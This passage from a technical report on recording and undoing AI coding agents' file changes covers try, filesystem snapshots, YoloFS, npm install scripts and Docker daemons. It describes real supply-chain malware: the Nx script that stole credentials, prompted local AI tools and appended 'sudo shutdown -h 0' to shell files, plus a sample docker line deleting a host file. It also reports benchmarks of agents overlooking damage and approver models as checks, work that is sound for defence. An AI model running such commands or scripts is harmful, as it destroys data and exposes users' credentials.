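A comparison of snapshots includes changes made by every process there, so it has the same attribution problem as a scan of the project folder, but over a larger area. If the developer edits `README.md` and reads a web page during `npm install`, a comparison of the home folder lists the edit and the browser's cache files alongside npm's packages, and a rollback would also discard the edit.

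A harness could reduce this problem by giving the agent a writable copy of the project, which Btrfs can create as a snapshot and ZFS as a clone. The copy shares unchanged blocks with the original, so it uses little space at first. If only the agent works in the copy, all changes there will be the agent's. Changes to files outside the project, such as `~/.bashrc`, would still affect the real files.

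Houssel and colleagues rate snapshot comparison as efficient but weak against attackers, who can act after one snapshot and remove the evidence before the next.

### The sample command

Suppose a developer on Linux runs `try ./setup.sh`. In a separate run without `try`, the harness takes ZFS or Btrfs snapshots of the home folder and `/srv/data` before the command and again when the shell returns. On a Mac, the harness takes an APFS snapshot before the command, mounts it and compares it with the current files as soon as the shell returns. Docker shares the folder containing `old.db` from the Data volume.

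| Effect | `try` | ZFS or Btrfs snapshots | APFS snapshot |
|---|---|---|---|
| 1. `src/config.json` overwritten | Old and new contents | Old and new contents | Old and new contents |
| 2. `notes.md` moved | Deletion and creation | Move | Deletion and creation |
| 3. Temporary file | Nothing | Nothing | Nothing |
| 4. Line added to `~/.bashrc` | Old and new contents | Old and new contents | Old and new contents |
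| 5. `.env` read | Nothing without `-t` | Nothing | Nothing |
| 6. HTTPS request | Nothing | Nothing | Nothing |
| 7. `old.db` deleted | Not held back | Deletion, with old contents | Deletion, with old contents |
| 8. `cache.bin` written later | Probably never written | Nothing, if written after the second snapshot | Nothing, if written after the comparison |

Under `try`, the line added to `~/.bashrc` reaches the real file only if the user accepts it. The user can accept the changes to the project and leave that one out. But the list also includes the new packages in `node_modules`, and a user who accepts them also accepts the package whose install script added the line.

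Deleting `old.db` is more dangerous. If the `docker` command can reach `dockerd` from inside the overlay, the container deletes the real file, because `dockerd` runs outside the overlay. The user could then reject every change on the list and still lose the database. The snapshots would preserve it but would not link the deletion to the agent.

The background process is unlikely to survive under `try`. It runs in a separate PID namespace, and when the namespace's first process exits, the kernel kills the rest. If that happens before the background process has written `cache.bin`, the file will be missing from the list the user reviews, and the project may lack it even though an ordinary run would have produced it.

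## How YoloFS records file changes so that they can be undone

YoloFS, which Zhong and colleagues presented at the operating-systems conference SOSP in 2026, keeps a log of changes and leaves the original files in place until the user accepts the new ones. Overlays and snapshots show what changed, but not the operations behind the changes. A recorder can work out what changed from a log of system calls, but that log alone can't restore a file.

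### From a log of system calls to a change set

Suppose a script in `/home/ana/app` replaces `src/config.json` the way many programs save files, by writing a temporary file and renaming it over the old one. A shortened strace log could look like this:

```
openat(AT_FDCWD, "local.json", O_RDONLY) = -1 ENOENT (No such file or directory)
openat(AT_FDCWD, "src", O_RDONLY|O_DIRECTORY) = 3
openat(3, "config.tmp", O_WRONLY|O_CREAT|O_EXCL, 0644) = 4
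write(4, "{\"port\": 8080}\n", 15) = 15
renameat(3, "config.tmp", 3, "config.json") = 0
openat(AT_FDCWD, "setup.log", O_WRONLY|O_CREAT|O_TRUNC, 0644) = 5
unlink("setup.log") = 0
```

A program can reduce this log to a change set in five steps:

1. Keep only the successful calls. The first call failed because `local.json` doesn't exist, so it changed nothing.
2. Work out each file's full path. File descriptor 3 stands for the folder `src`, so the temporary file is `/home/ana/app/src/config.tmp`. The program has to keep track of every change of working directory and every open descriptor, including those that child processes inherit. It also has to resolve symbolic links, or it will list a change under the wrong path.
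3. Follow renames and hard links. The data written to `config.tmp` ends up in `config.json`. If a file has two names, a write through one changes what both show, so the program should identify files by inode.
4. Cancel files that the command created and then deleted. `setup.log` belongs here only if it is new. `O_CREAT` also opens a file that already exists, so this log can't settle the question. If there was an older `setup.log`, the net change is a deletion.
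5. Put the remaining changes in order. An undo has to work backwards. If a script deletes `a` and then renames `b` to `a`, the undo must rename `a` back to `b` before it restores the old `a`. Otherwise the restored file overwrites the only copy of `b`.

If `setup.log` was new, the only remaining change is the replacement of `src/config.json`. A single lost event can distort this result. If the rename event were lost, the change set would list a new `config.tmp` that no longer exists and leave out the change to `config.json`.

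### Saving the old contents first

Even a complete log isn't enough to reverse the change to `config.json`. The rename removed the old file's name, and the kernel normally frees a file's data once the file has no name and no process has it open. Opening a file with `O_TRUNC`, as the sample command does, also destroys the old contents. Logging every byte the program writes would preserve only the new text.

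A recorder therefore has to save the pre-image before the kernel carries out the call. What it needs depends on the operation:

| Operation | Save beforehand | To undo |
|---|---|---|
| Create a file | Nothing | Delete it |
| Open an existing file for writing | Contents | Put the contents back |
| Delete a file | Contents, owner and permissions | Recreate it |
| Rename to an unused name | Nothing | Rename it back |
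| Rename over an existing file | The existing file's contents, owner and permissions | Rename back, then recreate the replaced file |
| Change permissions | Old permissions | Set them again |

Before a deletion or a rename over an existing file, the recorder can avoid copying the old file by giving it a second name with a hard link. The data then survives when the first name is removed. This doesn't work for truncation, because both names refer to the same inode and would both show an empty file.

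OpenDev, the agent in *Building Effective AI Coding Agents for the Terminal*, logs each operation by its own edit tools along with the file's previous content. It keeps a limited number of entries, on the grounds that users rarely undo operations older than the last dozen or so. For shell commands, a recorder needs a way to pause the process while it copies the old content, such as the stops that strace uses.

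### How YoloFS stores changes

Like OverlayFS, YoloFS writes new contents to a separate place. It never lets the agent change the original files, so it doesn't need to back them up.

YoloFS is a kernel module that sits on top of an existing file system, which Zhong and colleagues call the base. A hook, a harness feature that runs a program before each tool call, passes the agent's command to `yolo run`, which starts it in its own mount namespace with YoloFS as the root of the folder tree. All the command's file accesses, inside and outside the project, then go through YoloFS. It records operations in the kernel, and only those that take effect, so it doesn't have to reconstruct paths or discard failed calls afterwards.

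It keeps three structures:

- The flat file store is a folder that holds the contents of new and changed files. YoloFS identifies each file by a number, so its place in the store doesn't depend on its path.
- The override tree, in the kernel's memory, maps paths to contents. A path can point to a numbered file in the store, to a location in the base, or to nothing, which means that the file no longer exists for the agent. For a path without an entry, the agent sees the base file.
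- The journal is a file to which the kernel adds a record whenever the override tree changes. The records are stage (`S`), delete (`D`) and rename (`R`), and each includes what the path pointed to before.

When a program opens an existing file for writing, YoloFS first copies the file to the store. If the program opens it with truncation, YoloFS creates an empty file there instead. A rename copies nothing, because the new path can point to the old location in the base, whereas OverlayFS copies the whole file.

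### Six system calls, step by step

In the paper's example, a folder `a` contains the files `x`, `y` and `z`, and the agent's command makes six system calls. In the records, `∅` means "nothing".

| Call | Journal record | Override tree |
|---|---|---|
| 1. Open `a/x` with truncation | `S a/x 1 a/x` | `a/x` points to stored file 1, which is empty |
| 2. Write to `a/x` | No record | No change; the data goes to stored file 1 |
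| 3. Delete `a/y` | `D a/y a/y` | `a/y` points to nothing |
| 4. Rename `a/x` to `a/y` | `R a/x a/y 1 ∅` | `a/y` points to stored file 1, and `a/x` to nothing |
| 5. Create folder `c` | `S c/ 2 ∅` | `c` points to stored folder 2 |
| 6. Rename `a` to `c/b` | `R a/ c/b/ a/ ∅` | `c/b` points to the base folder `a`, and `a` to nothing |

In the first record, `1` is the number of the new stored file, and the final `a/x` is the previous state, which was the original file in the base. The fourth record ends with the previous states of two paths. `a/x` pointed to stored file 1, and `a/y` pointed to nothing because the third call had deleted it.

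The agent now sees a folder `c/b` with the files `y` and `z`. On the disk, `a` still contains all three files with their old contents.

A review of these changes shows that `a` became `c/b`, that `x` is gone and that `y` has new contents. The command deleted the original `y` and moved another file into its place, but the review omits these steps because it compares only the final state with the original. The journal records each step.

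### Review, commit and abort

At the end of a session, the user runs `yolo review`, which replays the journal, rebuilds the override tree and compares each path in it with the base. In one of the paper's examples, a script adds an attacker's key to `~/.ssh/authorized_keys`, deletes the system's audit log and moves itself to `~/.bashrc`. The review lists all three changes and shows the added key.

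The user can then leave the changes staged, abort or commit:

- To abort, YoloFS empties the override tree, the store and the journal. The base needs no repair.
- To commit, YoloFS applies the final state of each path. It puts a stored file in place, moves a base file to its new name or deletes it. If the agent swapped the names of two files, moving either one directly would overwrite the other, so YoloFS moves them through temporary names.

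The agent can't do either, because the kernel checks the root file system of the calling process and rejects these requests from any process inside the YoloFS mount.

A commit replaces the originals, so the user can no longer recover them through YoloFS. It could also overwrite edits that the user made to the same files during the session. Zhong and colleagues leave conflicts between concurrent sessions to other tools. Hard links may also cause problems because the override tree tracks files by path. A write through one of a file's names might not appear under the others, as in OverlayFS by default. The paper doesn't discuss this case.

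### Going back without losing history

By default, YoloFS takes a snapshot after every command by adding a marker to the journal. The records between two markers show what one command did. For each path, the first record gives the state before the command, and the last gives the state after it. YoloFS can therefore list a command's changes without replaying the whole session.

A snapshot also has to preserve file contents. YoloFS gives each stored file a generation number, which goes up at every marker. When a program opens a file from an earlier generation for writing, YoloFS makes a new copy and leaves the older one unchanged. The store therefore gains one version of a file for each command that writes to it, no matter how many times that command writes.

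The agent can return to any snapshot, which Zhong and colleagues call traveling. Suppose it runs commands A and B, decides that B was a mistake and travels back to the snapshot after A. YoloFS rebuilds the override tree from A's records and adds a travel marker to the journal. If the agent then runs command C and finds that it needed B, it can travel to the snapshot after B, and YoloFS rebuilds the tree from A's and B's records. C's records stay in the journal, where the user can inspect them. A ZFS rollback, by contrast, discards everything after the chosen snapshot, including the evidence of what went wrong.

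*Design and implementation* describes an earlier version of YoloFS that treats Git commands like any other file operations, so an agent can recover uncommitted work after `git reset --hard` or repair a damaged `.git` folder.

Staging can't undo a program reading a password, so YoloFS also has access rules for paths. Under the `ask` policy, the kernel pauses the program and shows the user the path, the operation and the process name. The user can save the answer as a rule for later accesses. If nobody answers in time, YoloFS refuses the access. The journal records each prompt and refusal, but not reads that a rule already allows.

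### Tests with hidden damage and routine tasks

Zhong and colleagues tested whether an agent would notice damage that it had not asked for. They prepared 11 projects, each with 10 to 41 lines of code, and gave Claude Code a routine request in each, such as running a linter (a program that checks code for errors). The tool did its job but also damaged other files, as in YoloFS-Ext, the benchmark that grew out of these projects. The harmful code ranged from a readable script to a compiled program. After each command, YoloFS gave the agent a summary of the changed files, but the researchers did not tell it to look for damage.

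In 8 of the 11 tasks, the agent travelled back on its own. When a compiled linter deleted two source files, for example, the agent remarked that this was unusual for such a tool and restored them. In the other 3, it accepted the damage:

- A deployment script copied the source code to a staging folder and then deleted `src/`. The agent noticed the deletion but took it for normal deployment behavior.
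- An install script overwrote `config.json` and `.env` with production defaults, which the agent considered safe.
- A repair tool reset two settings files, and the agent took the changes for the requested fixes.

With YoloFS, the original files were still in the base in all 11 tasks, so a user could have rejected the changes. Without YoloFS, Claude Code let the damage happen in 10 tasks. In the remaining task, it decompiled the program and asked the user first.

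No user took part in the test, so it doesn't show how many people would have caught the remaining three. These projects were also small enough for the missing files to stand out. In a session that installs thousands of packages, a deleted `src/` would be much easier to overlook.

The second test measured interruptions across 112 tasks, each a single operation such as copying or deleting a file inside or outside the project. The test program approved every request and chose "don't ask again" where it could.

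| System | Tasks completed | User interactions per task |
|---|---|---|
| Claude Code with YoloFS | 99% | 0.4 |
| Claude Code | 98% | 0.9 |
| Codex | 100% | 0.4 |
| Copilot | 96% | 1.3 |
| Gemini CLI | 75% | 2.2 |

YoloFS prompted the user about half as often as Claude Code alone, mainly because it lets commands change the project freely and holds the changes for review. Codex prompted the user just as rarely, but it allows writes in the project without holding them for review. Since the test program approved every prompt, the results don't show whether people would answer YoloFS's prompts more carefully than ordinary approval prompts.

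### Speed compared with Ext4 and OverlayFS

Zhong and colleagues tested YoloFS on a Linux machine with a solid-state drive, using Ext4, a common Linux file system, as the base. For reads and writes on a 1 GB file, YoloFS stayed within 2% of Ext4's speed. OverlayFS was about as fast as Ext4 when reading data from the drive, but 19% to 23% slower when the data was already in memory and 12% to 15% slower for writes. The file was already staged in these tests, so the results exclude the time YoloFS takes to copy a large original when a program first opens it for writing.

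Snapshots made a larger difference. OverlayFS needs another layer for each one, and it failed at about 50 because the list of layers became too long for the mount command. Before that, each added layer made creating files and reading untouched ones slower. YoloFS keeps only the current override tree in the kernel, so those operations took the same time regardless of the number of snapshots. YoloFS commits do take longer with more snapshots.

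The most realistic test followed a developer working on the Linux kernel, with repeated searches, edits, builds and Git commits. YoloFS was as fast as Ext4 except for an extra 3.5 seconds at the end, when it committed more than 100,000 files. OverlayFS was 18% slower than YoloFS. The test didn't include a large `npm install`, but the size of the final commit suggests that one would be manageable.

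Installing YoloFS is a bigger obstacle than its speed. It requires a kernel module, which supports Linux 6.8 and 7.0, the default kernels in two Ubuntu releases. It doesn't run directly on macOS or Windows.

### Leaving the judgment to the agent

Wu and colleagues later tested YoloFS on the 102 dangerous tasks of YoloFS-Ext, alongside Caper and its separate approver model. They recreated YoloFS's agent interface in a container rather than installing the file system. The agent, GLM-5.3-Flash running in Claude Code, got a summary of changes after each command and five commands for inspecting and reverting those changes. The researchers turned off permission requests and judged the staged files before any user review.

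The harm rate with YoloFS was 35.3%, about half the rate for the same model without approval. That comparison isn't exact because the run without approval used a simpler harness. But in the same harness as YoloFS, the harm rate was 62.7% with Claude Code's own approval classifier, which suggests that most of the improvement came from showing the agent its changes.

The agent reverted something in 66 of the 102 tasks, and 3 of those ended in harm. Of the 36 tasks in which it reverted nothing, 33 ended in harm. Most of the harm came from runs in which the agent saw the list of changes and carried on.

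Wu and colleagues conclude that a judge outside the agent should review changes before they are final. With Caper's separate approver, only 6.9% of tasks ended in harm in Claude Code with the same agent model, but the separation may not be the only reason. Caper's approver was also a different model, GPT-5.6 Luna, and the report it saw included the changed lines of small text files. With the weaker approver that Wu and colleagues tried, Caper left almost as much harm as YoloFS. A fairer test would use the same model as agent and approver and show it the same report in both roles.

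The separate approver, Caper, also had the advantage of giving the agent a reason when it stopped a command. In Claude Code, the agent completed 40.2% of the tasks without harm with Caper and 22.5% with YoloFS. In 43 of the 102 YoloFS runs, the project was undamaged at the end but the task was unfinished.

On the broader SABER benchmark, 21.2% of tasks ended in harm with YoloFS, compared with 19.7% without approval. Wu and colleagues explain, correctly, that a password can't be taken back once the agent has sent it. But the difference is small enough to be chance, and the permission requests that YoloFS relies on to protect secrets were turned off in the test. SABER also judges the commands that the agent ran, so it may count a deletion as harmful even if the agent later reversed it. This might be why YoloFS had the worst result of any system on SABER's tasks about destroying files, the kind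 of damage it should be best at undoing.

In real use, the originals would have survived in the base in all 36 harmed YoloFS-Ext tasks, and a user who read the review carefully could still have aborted. YoloFS is therefore safer than the 35.3% figure implies, but it relies on people for the final check. In 80 of the 290 reports that Zhong and colleagues studied, the user had let the agent act without approval. A harness could instead send each command's journal records to a second model and return to the previous snapshot if that model rejects them. This would combine YoloFS's low-overhead snapshots with Caper's separate approver, though neither team has tested it.

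### The sample command

Suppose the agent runs `./setup.sh` through `yolo run`. YoloFS allows all accesses inside the project folder and prompts the user about any others, which the user approves. The temporary file is in the project folder.

| Effect | YoloFS's record | Can the user undo it? |
|---|---|---|
| 1. `src/config.json` overwritten | Stage record, old and new contents | Yes, until the commit |
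| 2. `notes.md` moved | Rename record with both names | Yes, until the commit |
| 3. Temporary file | Stage and delete records | Nothing to undo |
| 4. Line added to `~/.bashrc` | Permission request, stage record, old and new contents | Yes, until the commit |
| 5. `.env` read | Nothing | No |
| 6. HTTPS request | Nothing | No |
| 7. `old.db` deleted | Nothing | No |
| 8. `cache.bin` written later | Stage record, probably under the next command | Yes, until the commit |

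The temporary file appears in the journal but not in the review, because the final state is the same as the original.

The request about `~/.bashrc` lets the user stop the install script before it writes. It shows the name of the process, such as `sh`, but not which npm package started it. If the user had already allowed access to the whole home folder so that npm could use its cache, there would be no request. YoloFS would still stage the change, but the user would have to find it in a review that also lists every file in `node_modules`. The journal's records don't identify the process, so the review links the change to `./setup.sh` but not to npm.

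A rule that denies access to `.env` would block the read and add a note to the journal, so the script couldn't include the file's passwords in its HTTPS request. As under `try`, the container deletes the real `old.db` outside the staged view, so aborting the session doesn't restore it.

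## What npm install and other package installers change

An `npm install` fills event queues, audit logs and change reviews with thousands of routine entries, which makes one harmful write easy to miss. npm is the package manager that comes with Node.js. A package is a bundle of published code, and most packages depend on others, so a project with 20 direct dependencies can easily install several hundred.

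### One npm install from start to finish

Suppose an agent runs `npm install esbuild` in a project that uses Git:

1. npm reads `package.json`, the project's list of direct dependencies, and `package-lock.json`, which holds the exact version of every package from the last install. It queries the registry, npm's public server, about any package that is not in the lock file.
2. It downloads the missing packages as compressed archives, checks them against their hashes and stores them in a cache in the home folder.
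3. It unpacks the packages into `node_modules` in the project folder.
4. It runs the install scripts that its settings allow. A package can have a `preinstall`, an `install` and a `postinstall` script.
5. It updates `package-lock.json` and adds esbuild to `package.json`.

An install script is a shell command that the package's author chose. Many are harmless, such as esbuild's, which puts the right compiled program for the machine in place. But according to Semgrep's *RIP post/preinstall scripts*, these commands run with the full privileges of whoever ran `npm install` and can come from packages the developer never chose directly. A script can therefore change any file the developer can change.

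| What changes | Where | Does `git diff` show it? | Does `npm uninstall` reverse it? |
|---|---|---|---|
| List of dependencies | `package.json` | Yes | Yes |
| Exact versions | `package-lock.json` | Yes | Yes |
| The packages' files | `node_modules` | No | Yes |
| Downloaded archives | `~/.npm/_cacache` | No | No |
| Log of the install | `~/.npm/_logs` | No | No |
| Files that install scripts write | Anywhere the user can write | Only changes to tracked files | Only inside the package's own folder |

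Projects normally have Git ignore `node_modules`, so `git diff` also omits anything a script changed there. It doesn't show changes to the cache, the logs or `~/.bashrc` either, because they are outside the project.

npm sets `hasInstallScript` in the lock file for each package that has an install script, so a reviewer can see in `git diff` that a new package may run code, but not what the code does.

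### Which installers run a package's code by default

Before version 12, npm ran the install scripts of all dependencies by default. The last releases before version 12 had a list of approved packages, but Debian's *npm-approve-scripts* describes that list as advisory, and unapproved scripts still ran.

npm 12, released in July 2026, skips them. According to GitHub's *Upcoming breaking changes for npm v12* (2026), this includes the compile step that npm otherwise runs for packages with native code, even if they have no install script. npm 12 also refuses dependencies that come from a Git repository or a web address unless the user allows them. A package from Git could contain a settings file that replaced the Git program npm uses, and so run code even for users who had turned scripts off.

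npm stores approvals in the `allowScripts` field of `package.json`, which GitHub advises developers to commit, so if an agent approves a package to get a build working, the approval appears in `git diff`. An agent could also run `npm install-scripts approve --all`, which would leave a reviewer with a long list to check. A project downloaded from a stranger can arrive with its approvals already filled in. The block on install scripts covers only dependencies, not the project's own install scripts.

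pnpm, an alternative to npm, has blocked dependencies' scripts by default since version 10 in January 2025, according to Stephane Robert's blog. Since version 11, from April 2026, it also refuses any package version less than 24 hours old.

pip, the standard installer for Python packages, usually downloads a wheel, an archive that it only has to unpack. If a package has no wheel for the user's system, pip downloads the source code and runs the package's build code with the user's rights. It does this by default, and the option `--only-binary :all:` prevents it. Even a wheel can cause code to run later, because it can include a `.pth` file with lines that Python normally executes every time it starts.

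### Programs that several projects share

`npm install -g typescript` installs the TypeScript compiler for the whole machine or user account. Any project that relies on the global copy gets the new version, and its next build may fail even though nothing in its folder has changed. pip has the same effect outside a virtual environment, which is a folder with its own set of Python packages. Many Linux distributions make pip refuse such installs, but an agent can override this with `--break-system-packages`.

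Homebrew, the most common package manager on macOS, can upgrade libraries that other programs use when it installs a new program. On Debian and Ubuntu, apt runs the packages' own scripts as root. Its log in `/var/log/apt/history.log` lists the command and the package versions, but not the files those scripts changed.

In one report that Zhong and colleagues collected, an agent trying to fix a missing header file, a piece of code that a compiler needs, removed the entire toolchain. In another, an agent installing an MCP server, a program that gives agents extra tools, corrupted the settings file and then deleted it, along with the configurations and access tokens for all the user's other servers.

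The old version number is often enough to undo a global upgrade. A harness could save the output of `npm ls -g`, `pip freeze` and `brew list --versions` before and after each command. These lists are short, but they don't cover settings files like the one the agent deleted.

### The Nx attack of August 2025

On August 26, 2025, attackers used a stolen token to publish eight malicious versions of Nx, a build tool with about 6 million installs a week. The malicious versions were available for about four hours. OSV's *MAL-2025-41436* (2025), an entry in a public vulnerability database, reproduces the maintainers' advisory.

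The `postinstall` script searched the disk for text files and credentials. Strumpflohner adds in *S1ngularity*, the Nx team's review of the incident, that the script tried to prompt AI tools on the victim's machine, such as Claude and Gemini, to write the paths of configuration files to `/tmp/inventory.txt`. The script uploaded its findings to a new repository in the victim's own GitHub account. It also added `sudo shutdown -h 0` to `~/.bashrc` and `~/.zshrc`, so each new terminal asked for the user's password and shut down the machine if the user entered it.

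| What the script did | Records that would show it |
|---|---|
| Started as `node telemetry.js` | npm's log; process events from strace, Audit, Tetragon or Sysmon |
| Read credentials | strace; Audit, if it has rules for those files |
| Wrote `/tmp/inventory.txt` | File events; a before-and-after comparison that includes `/tmp` |
| Changed `~/.bashrc` and `~/.zshrc` | File events; a comparison of the home folder, with the old contents |
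| Gave a prompt to an AI tool | Process events; the AI tool's session files |
| Created a GitHub repository | The `gh` command in process events; the security log of the GitHub account |

A connection log would have helped less than usual, because developers' machines contact GitHub all day. `git diff` would have shown a new version number at most.

Semgrep's *Security Alert* advised users to search npm's logs for `telemetry.js` and Claude Code's session files for the malicious prompt. The session files would record the session the script started, not the session of an agent that ran `npm install`. By default, npm keeps logs of only its last ten runs, so on a busy machine the evidence there could disappear within a day.

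Some victims had no project that used Nx. A VS Code extension installed the latest version of the package just to check its version number, so opening the editor during those hours was enough to run the script. The advisory lists AI agents among the ways a package can get installed unnoticed. If an agent had been working at the same time, a recorder that attributes events by login would have mixed the editor's install with the agent's commands, while one that follows the process tree would have separated them.

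### Malicious packages that hide their traces

In May 2026, attackers published 84 malicious versions of 42 TanStack packages, which are widely used for building websites, within about six minutes. According to OSV's *GHSA-g7cv-rxg3-hmpx* (2026), the install went like this:

1. The malicious package listed `@tanstack/setup`, an invented package, as an optional dependency, with a Git address instead of a version number.
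2. npm downloaded it from there and ran its `prepare` script.
3. The script started the malware, which collected SSH keys, npm and GitHub tokens and cloud credentials, and sent them out through the servers of an encrypted messaging service.
4. The script then failed on purpose. npm discards an optional dependency that fails to install, so it left no `@tanstack/setup` folder in `node_modules`.

A comparison of the project folder, even one that included ignored files, would have missed this dependency. It would have found the malware's main file, about 2.3 MB of scrambled JavaScript, but only as one more file in a package that the user wanted. An event log would have recorded the script, the files it read and the connections. npm 12 would have blocked this route by refusing the Git address.

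The attack on axios, a popular library for web requests, hid its traces differently. In March 2026, attackers published versions that installed a malicious package called `plain-crypto-js`. After the install, that package's `package.json` listed no install script. UNU's *When Trust Becomes a Weapon* warns that neither running `npm audit` nor inspecting the folder would reveal the attack, and recommends checking logs of outgoing connections. The malicious version in axios's main release line was available for just under three hours, according to the axios maintainer's timeline, which Solar Designer (2026) posted to a security mailing list. pnpm's 24-hour wait would have protected users from it and from the Nx versions.

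The new defaults have not ended such attacks. On July 11, 2026, days after npm 12 came out, attackers published a version of the jscrambler package with a malicious `preinstall` script that unpacked a program into the system's temporary folder and ran it. SC Media's *Jscrambler npm package version 8.14.0 contained a malicious infostealer* (2026) reports that the attack bypassed npm's recent protections. But under npm 12's documented defaults, the script would run only in projects that had approved the package. Users of older versions had no such protection.

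### Installing packages in a sandbox first

The Open Source Security Foundation (OpenSSF), an industry group, runs a project that records what packages do before developers install them. OpenSSF's *Package Analysis* describes the process:

1. The system monitors package registries for new uploads and adds each one to a queue.
2. A worker runs the package in a container protected by gVisor, software that handles the container's system calls itself instead of passing them straight to the machine's kernel.
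3. strace logs the system calls, and a separate capture saves the network traffic.
4. The system stores which files the package accessed, which addresses it contacted and which commands it ran, in a public database.

The records also let researchers compare versions of a package. If a package that has never used the network contacts an unknown server during an install, that change is a warning sign.

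In 2022, Brown and Wheeler reported for OpenSSF that the prototype had found more than 200 malicious packages on npm and PyPI, the main Python registry, in one month. Most had names that resembled popular packages or matched companies' internal ones. Their install scripts typically sent the machine's name or the username to a server. Brown and Wheeler thought security researchers hoping for rewards had probably uploaded most of the packages, so the count is a poor measure of real attacks. According to Google's *The Package Analysis Project* (2022), the program analyzed all packages uploaded to popular repositories.

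Amazon's security researchers publish their findings in a related OpenSSF collection of reports. According to AWS, they had identified 188,550 malicious packages by May 13, 2026, all but 12 of them on npm. They found only 619 in April, so most of the total must come from earlier surges.

As with Caper's trial runs, a package may behave differently in the sandbox. The Nx script relied on the victim's GitHub login and AI tools, which a bare container would lack. The database is therefore best used as a warning before an agent installs a package, alongside a record of the real run.

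Packj, an older tool, works on the developer's own machine without a container or virtual machine. According to The Ruby Toolbox, it uses strace to keep install scripts away from sensitive files and then prints a summary of their activity, including network connections, for the user to review.

### Why uninstalling doesn't undo an install script

`npm uninstall nx` deletes the package's folder and its entries in `package.json` and `package-lock.json`. npm doesn't log which files an install script changed, and since version 7 it doesn't run uninstall scripts, so packages can't use them to undo those changes. The Nx team told users to delete the added lines from their shell files by hand, clear the npm, yarn and pnpm caches, and replace their credentials. For the TanStack packages, OSV's *MAL-2026-3466* (2026) warns that removing the package may not remove everything it installed.

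To reverse an install script's changes, a developer needs a record of:

- every file the script created, changed or deleted outside its package's folder, with the old contents
- processes that were still running when the install ended, and any files that would start them again
- the credential files that the script read, so the user knows which keys to replace
- the servers it contacted and any changes it made there, such as a new repository
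- the package responsible for each of these.

No recorder described so far provides all of this. YoloFS keeps old contents but doesn't log ordinary reads, while strace logs reads but doesn't keep old contents.

The order of cleanup matters too. According to Security Boulevard's *The TanStack npm supply chain attack that hit 170 packages* (2026), the malware left a script running that checked the stolen GitHub token every 60 seconds and deleted the user's home folder if the token stopped working. Revoking the token first, which is the standard advice, would have triggered the deletion. A process log would have shown the running script, so the user could have stopped it before revoking the token.

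Cancelling an install may not help either. *From Compromised Package to Cloud Breach* (Trent, 2026) describes a campaign against other npm packages in which the malware collected credentials even when the user cancelled the install after the script had started. A harness that saves its record only when a command finishes would save nothing from such a run.

### The sample command

When npm runs the install script that changes `~/.bashrc`, it logs the package's name and the script's command. As with Tetragon's events, the command may not contain the added line. Even then, a recorder such as Linux Audit can show when a process changed `~/.bashrc`, and npm's log can show which package's script was running at that time.

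npm's files contain nothing about the script's other seven effects. After the run, `git diff` shows the new `src/config.json`, the disappearance of `notes.md` and perhaps a changed lock file. Git lists `docs/notes.md` only in `git status`, as an untracked file. Uninstalling the package leaves the line in `~/.bashrc`.

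## Docker and other background services that act for the agent

A recorder that follows the agent's processes misses effect 7 of the sample command, because the process that deletes `/srv/data/old.db` doesn't descend from the agent's shell. The recorder can miss the effects of any service that was already running and accepts requests for the same reason.

### From the docker command to the deleted file

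Suppose `setup.sh` contains this line:

```
docker run --rm -v /srv/data:/data alpine rm /data/old.db
```

`-v` makes the real folder `/srv/data` available inside the container as `/data`, `alpine` is a small Linux image, and `--rm` removes the container when its command has finished. The deletion then goes like this:

1. `docker` turns the line into a JSON request containing the image, the command and the shared folder. It sends the request to `dockerd` through the local socket `/var/run/docker.sock`.
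2. `dockerd` replies with the new container's ID, and `docker` sends another request to start the container.
3. `dockerd` passes the job to containerd, a second permanently running service.
4. According to containerd's *Runtime V2*, containerd prepares the container's files and launches a helper program called a shim. The shim runs a further program, runc, to start the container.
5. runc starts `rm` inside the container and exits. `rm` deletes the file.

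Two separate process trees take part:

```
agent harness
└─ bash
   └─ setup.sh
      └─ docker run ...

systemd
├─ dockerd
├─ containerd
└─ containerd-shim-runc-v2
   └─ rm /data/old.db
```

The shim is normally a direct child of systemd, the first process on most Linux machines, because the process that launched it exits once the shim is running. The shim has registered to adopt orphaned processes, so it becomes the parent of `rm` when runc exits.

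A tracer attached to the agent's shell covers only the shell's own process tree, so the last evidence it records is the Docker client's exchange with the daemon over the socket. *How the docker container creation process works (from docker run to runc)* (2018) includes a trace of such an exchange, with the full JSON request and the container's ID in the reply. The command for that trace raised strace's limit to 8,192 bytes per read or write. At the default of 32 bytes, the log would cut off the request before the image name or the container's command.

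Docker's event log and Tetragon both use the container ID, so a recorder that saves the ID from Docker's reply can match the agent's request to the right container without relying on timing.

### Other services that act on request

Many other programs carry out work for a process that they didn't start:

- `systemd-run` asks systemd to start a command, which then runs outside the agent's process tree.
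- cron starts a scheduled job itself, perhaps days after the agent added the job to its list.
- launchd does the same on macOS for jobs that the agent installs.
- The build tools Gradle and Bazel keep a server running between builds, and that server does the work when a later command asks for it.
- A database server changes its own files when a client sends it an instruction such as `DROP TABLE`.
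- A terminal multiplexer such as tmux can type a command into a shell that the developer opened earlier.
- `ssh-agent` and `gpg-agent` sign data for programs that never read the key file, and Apache Magpie's *sandbox troubleshooting* reports that signed Git commits fail when a sandbox blocks the agent's socket.
- On macOS, a command can use Apple Events to make other applications act, which Claude Code's sandbox blocks by default, according to Anthropic.
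- Under WSL2, Linux hands the launch of a Windows program to Windows through a socket, so a recorder inside WSL2 misses what the program does.

By contrast, the script started the process that writes `cache.bin`, so a recorder that follows process creation can keep tracking that process after the tool call returns.

A Gradle server can be inside or outside the agent's process tree, depending on what started it. If the developer's editor started it, its writes during the agent's build are outside the tree. If the agent's build started it, those writes are inside the tree, but the developer's next build may reuse the server, and a recorder would then attribute the developer's output to the agent. A harness could run `gradle --stop` or `bazel shutdown` before and after a session, so that the agent and the developer each start their own server.

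King, Zhang and colleagues (2026), in *On the Effectiveness of Kernel-Level Evidence for Agent Security*, ran each agent session in a fresh container with strace attached to the first process, so any service that starts during the session descends from that process. In 10 trials with three sessions running at once, none of the 8,240 recorded events ended up in the wrong session's log. The method doesn't cover agents that were already running as permanent services when the tracer attached. It also wouldn't cover a new container requested through the host's Docker socket, because that container would be outside the traced one.

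### How Agent-Warden follows files between process trees

*Agent-Warden*, published in September 2026, describes an eBPF monitor that can connect two process trees if they share a file. It starts by marking the agent's process and then passes the mark on according to four rules:

1. A new process inherits the mark of the process that started it, and keeps the mark when it loads a different program.
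2. When a marked process writes data to a regular file, the file gets the mark. The mark belongs to the inode, so it survives a rename.
3. When an unmarked process reads data from a marked file, the process gets the mark.
4. When a marked process exits, its parent gets the mark.

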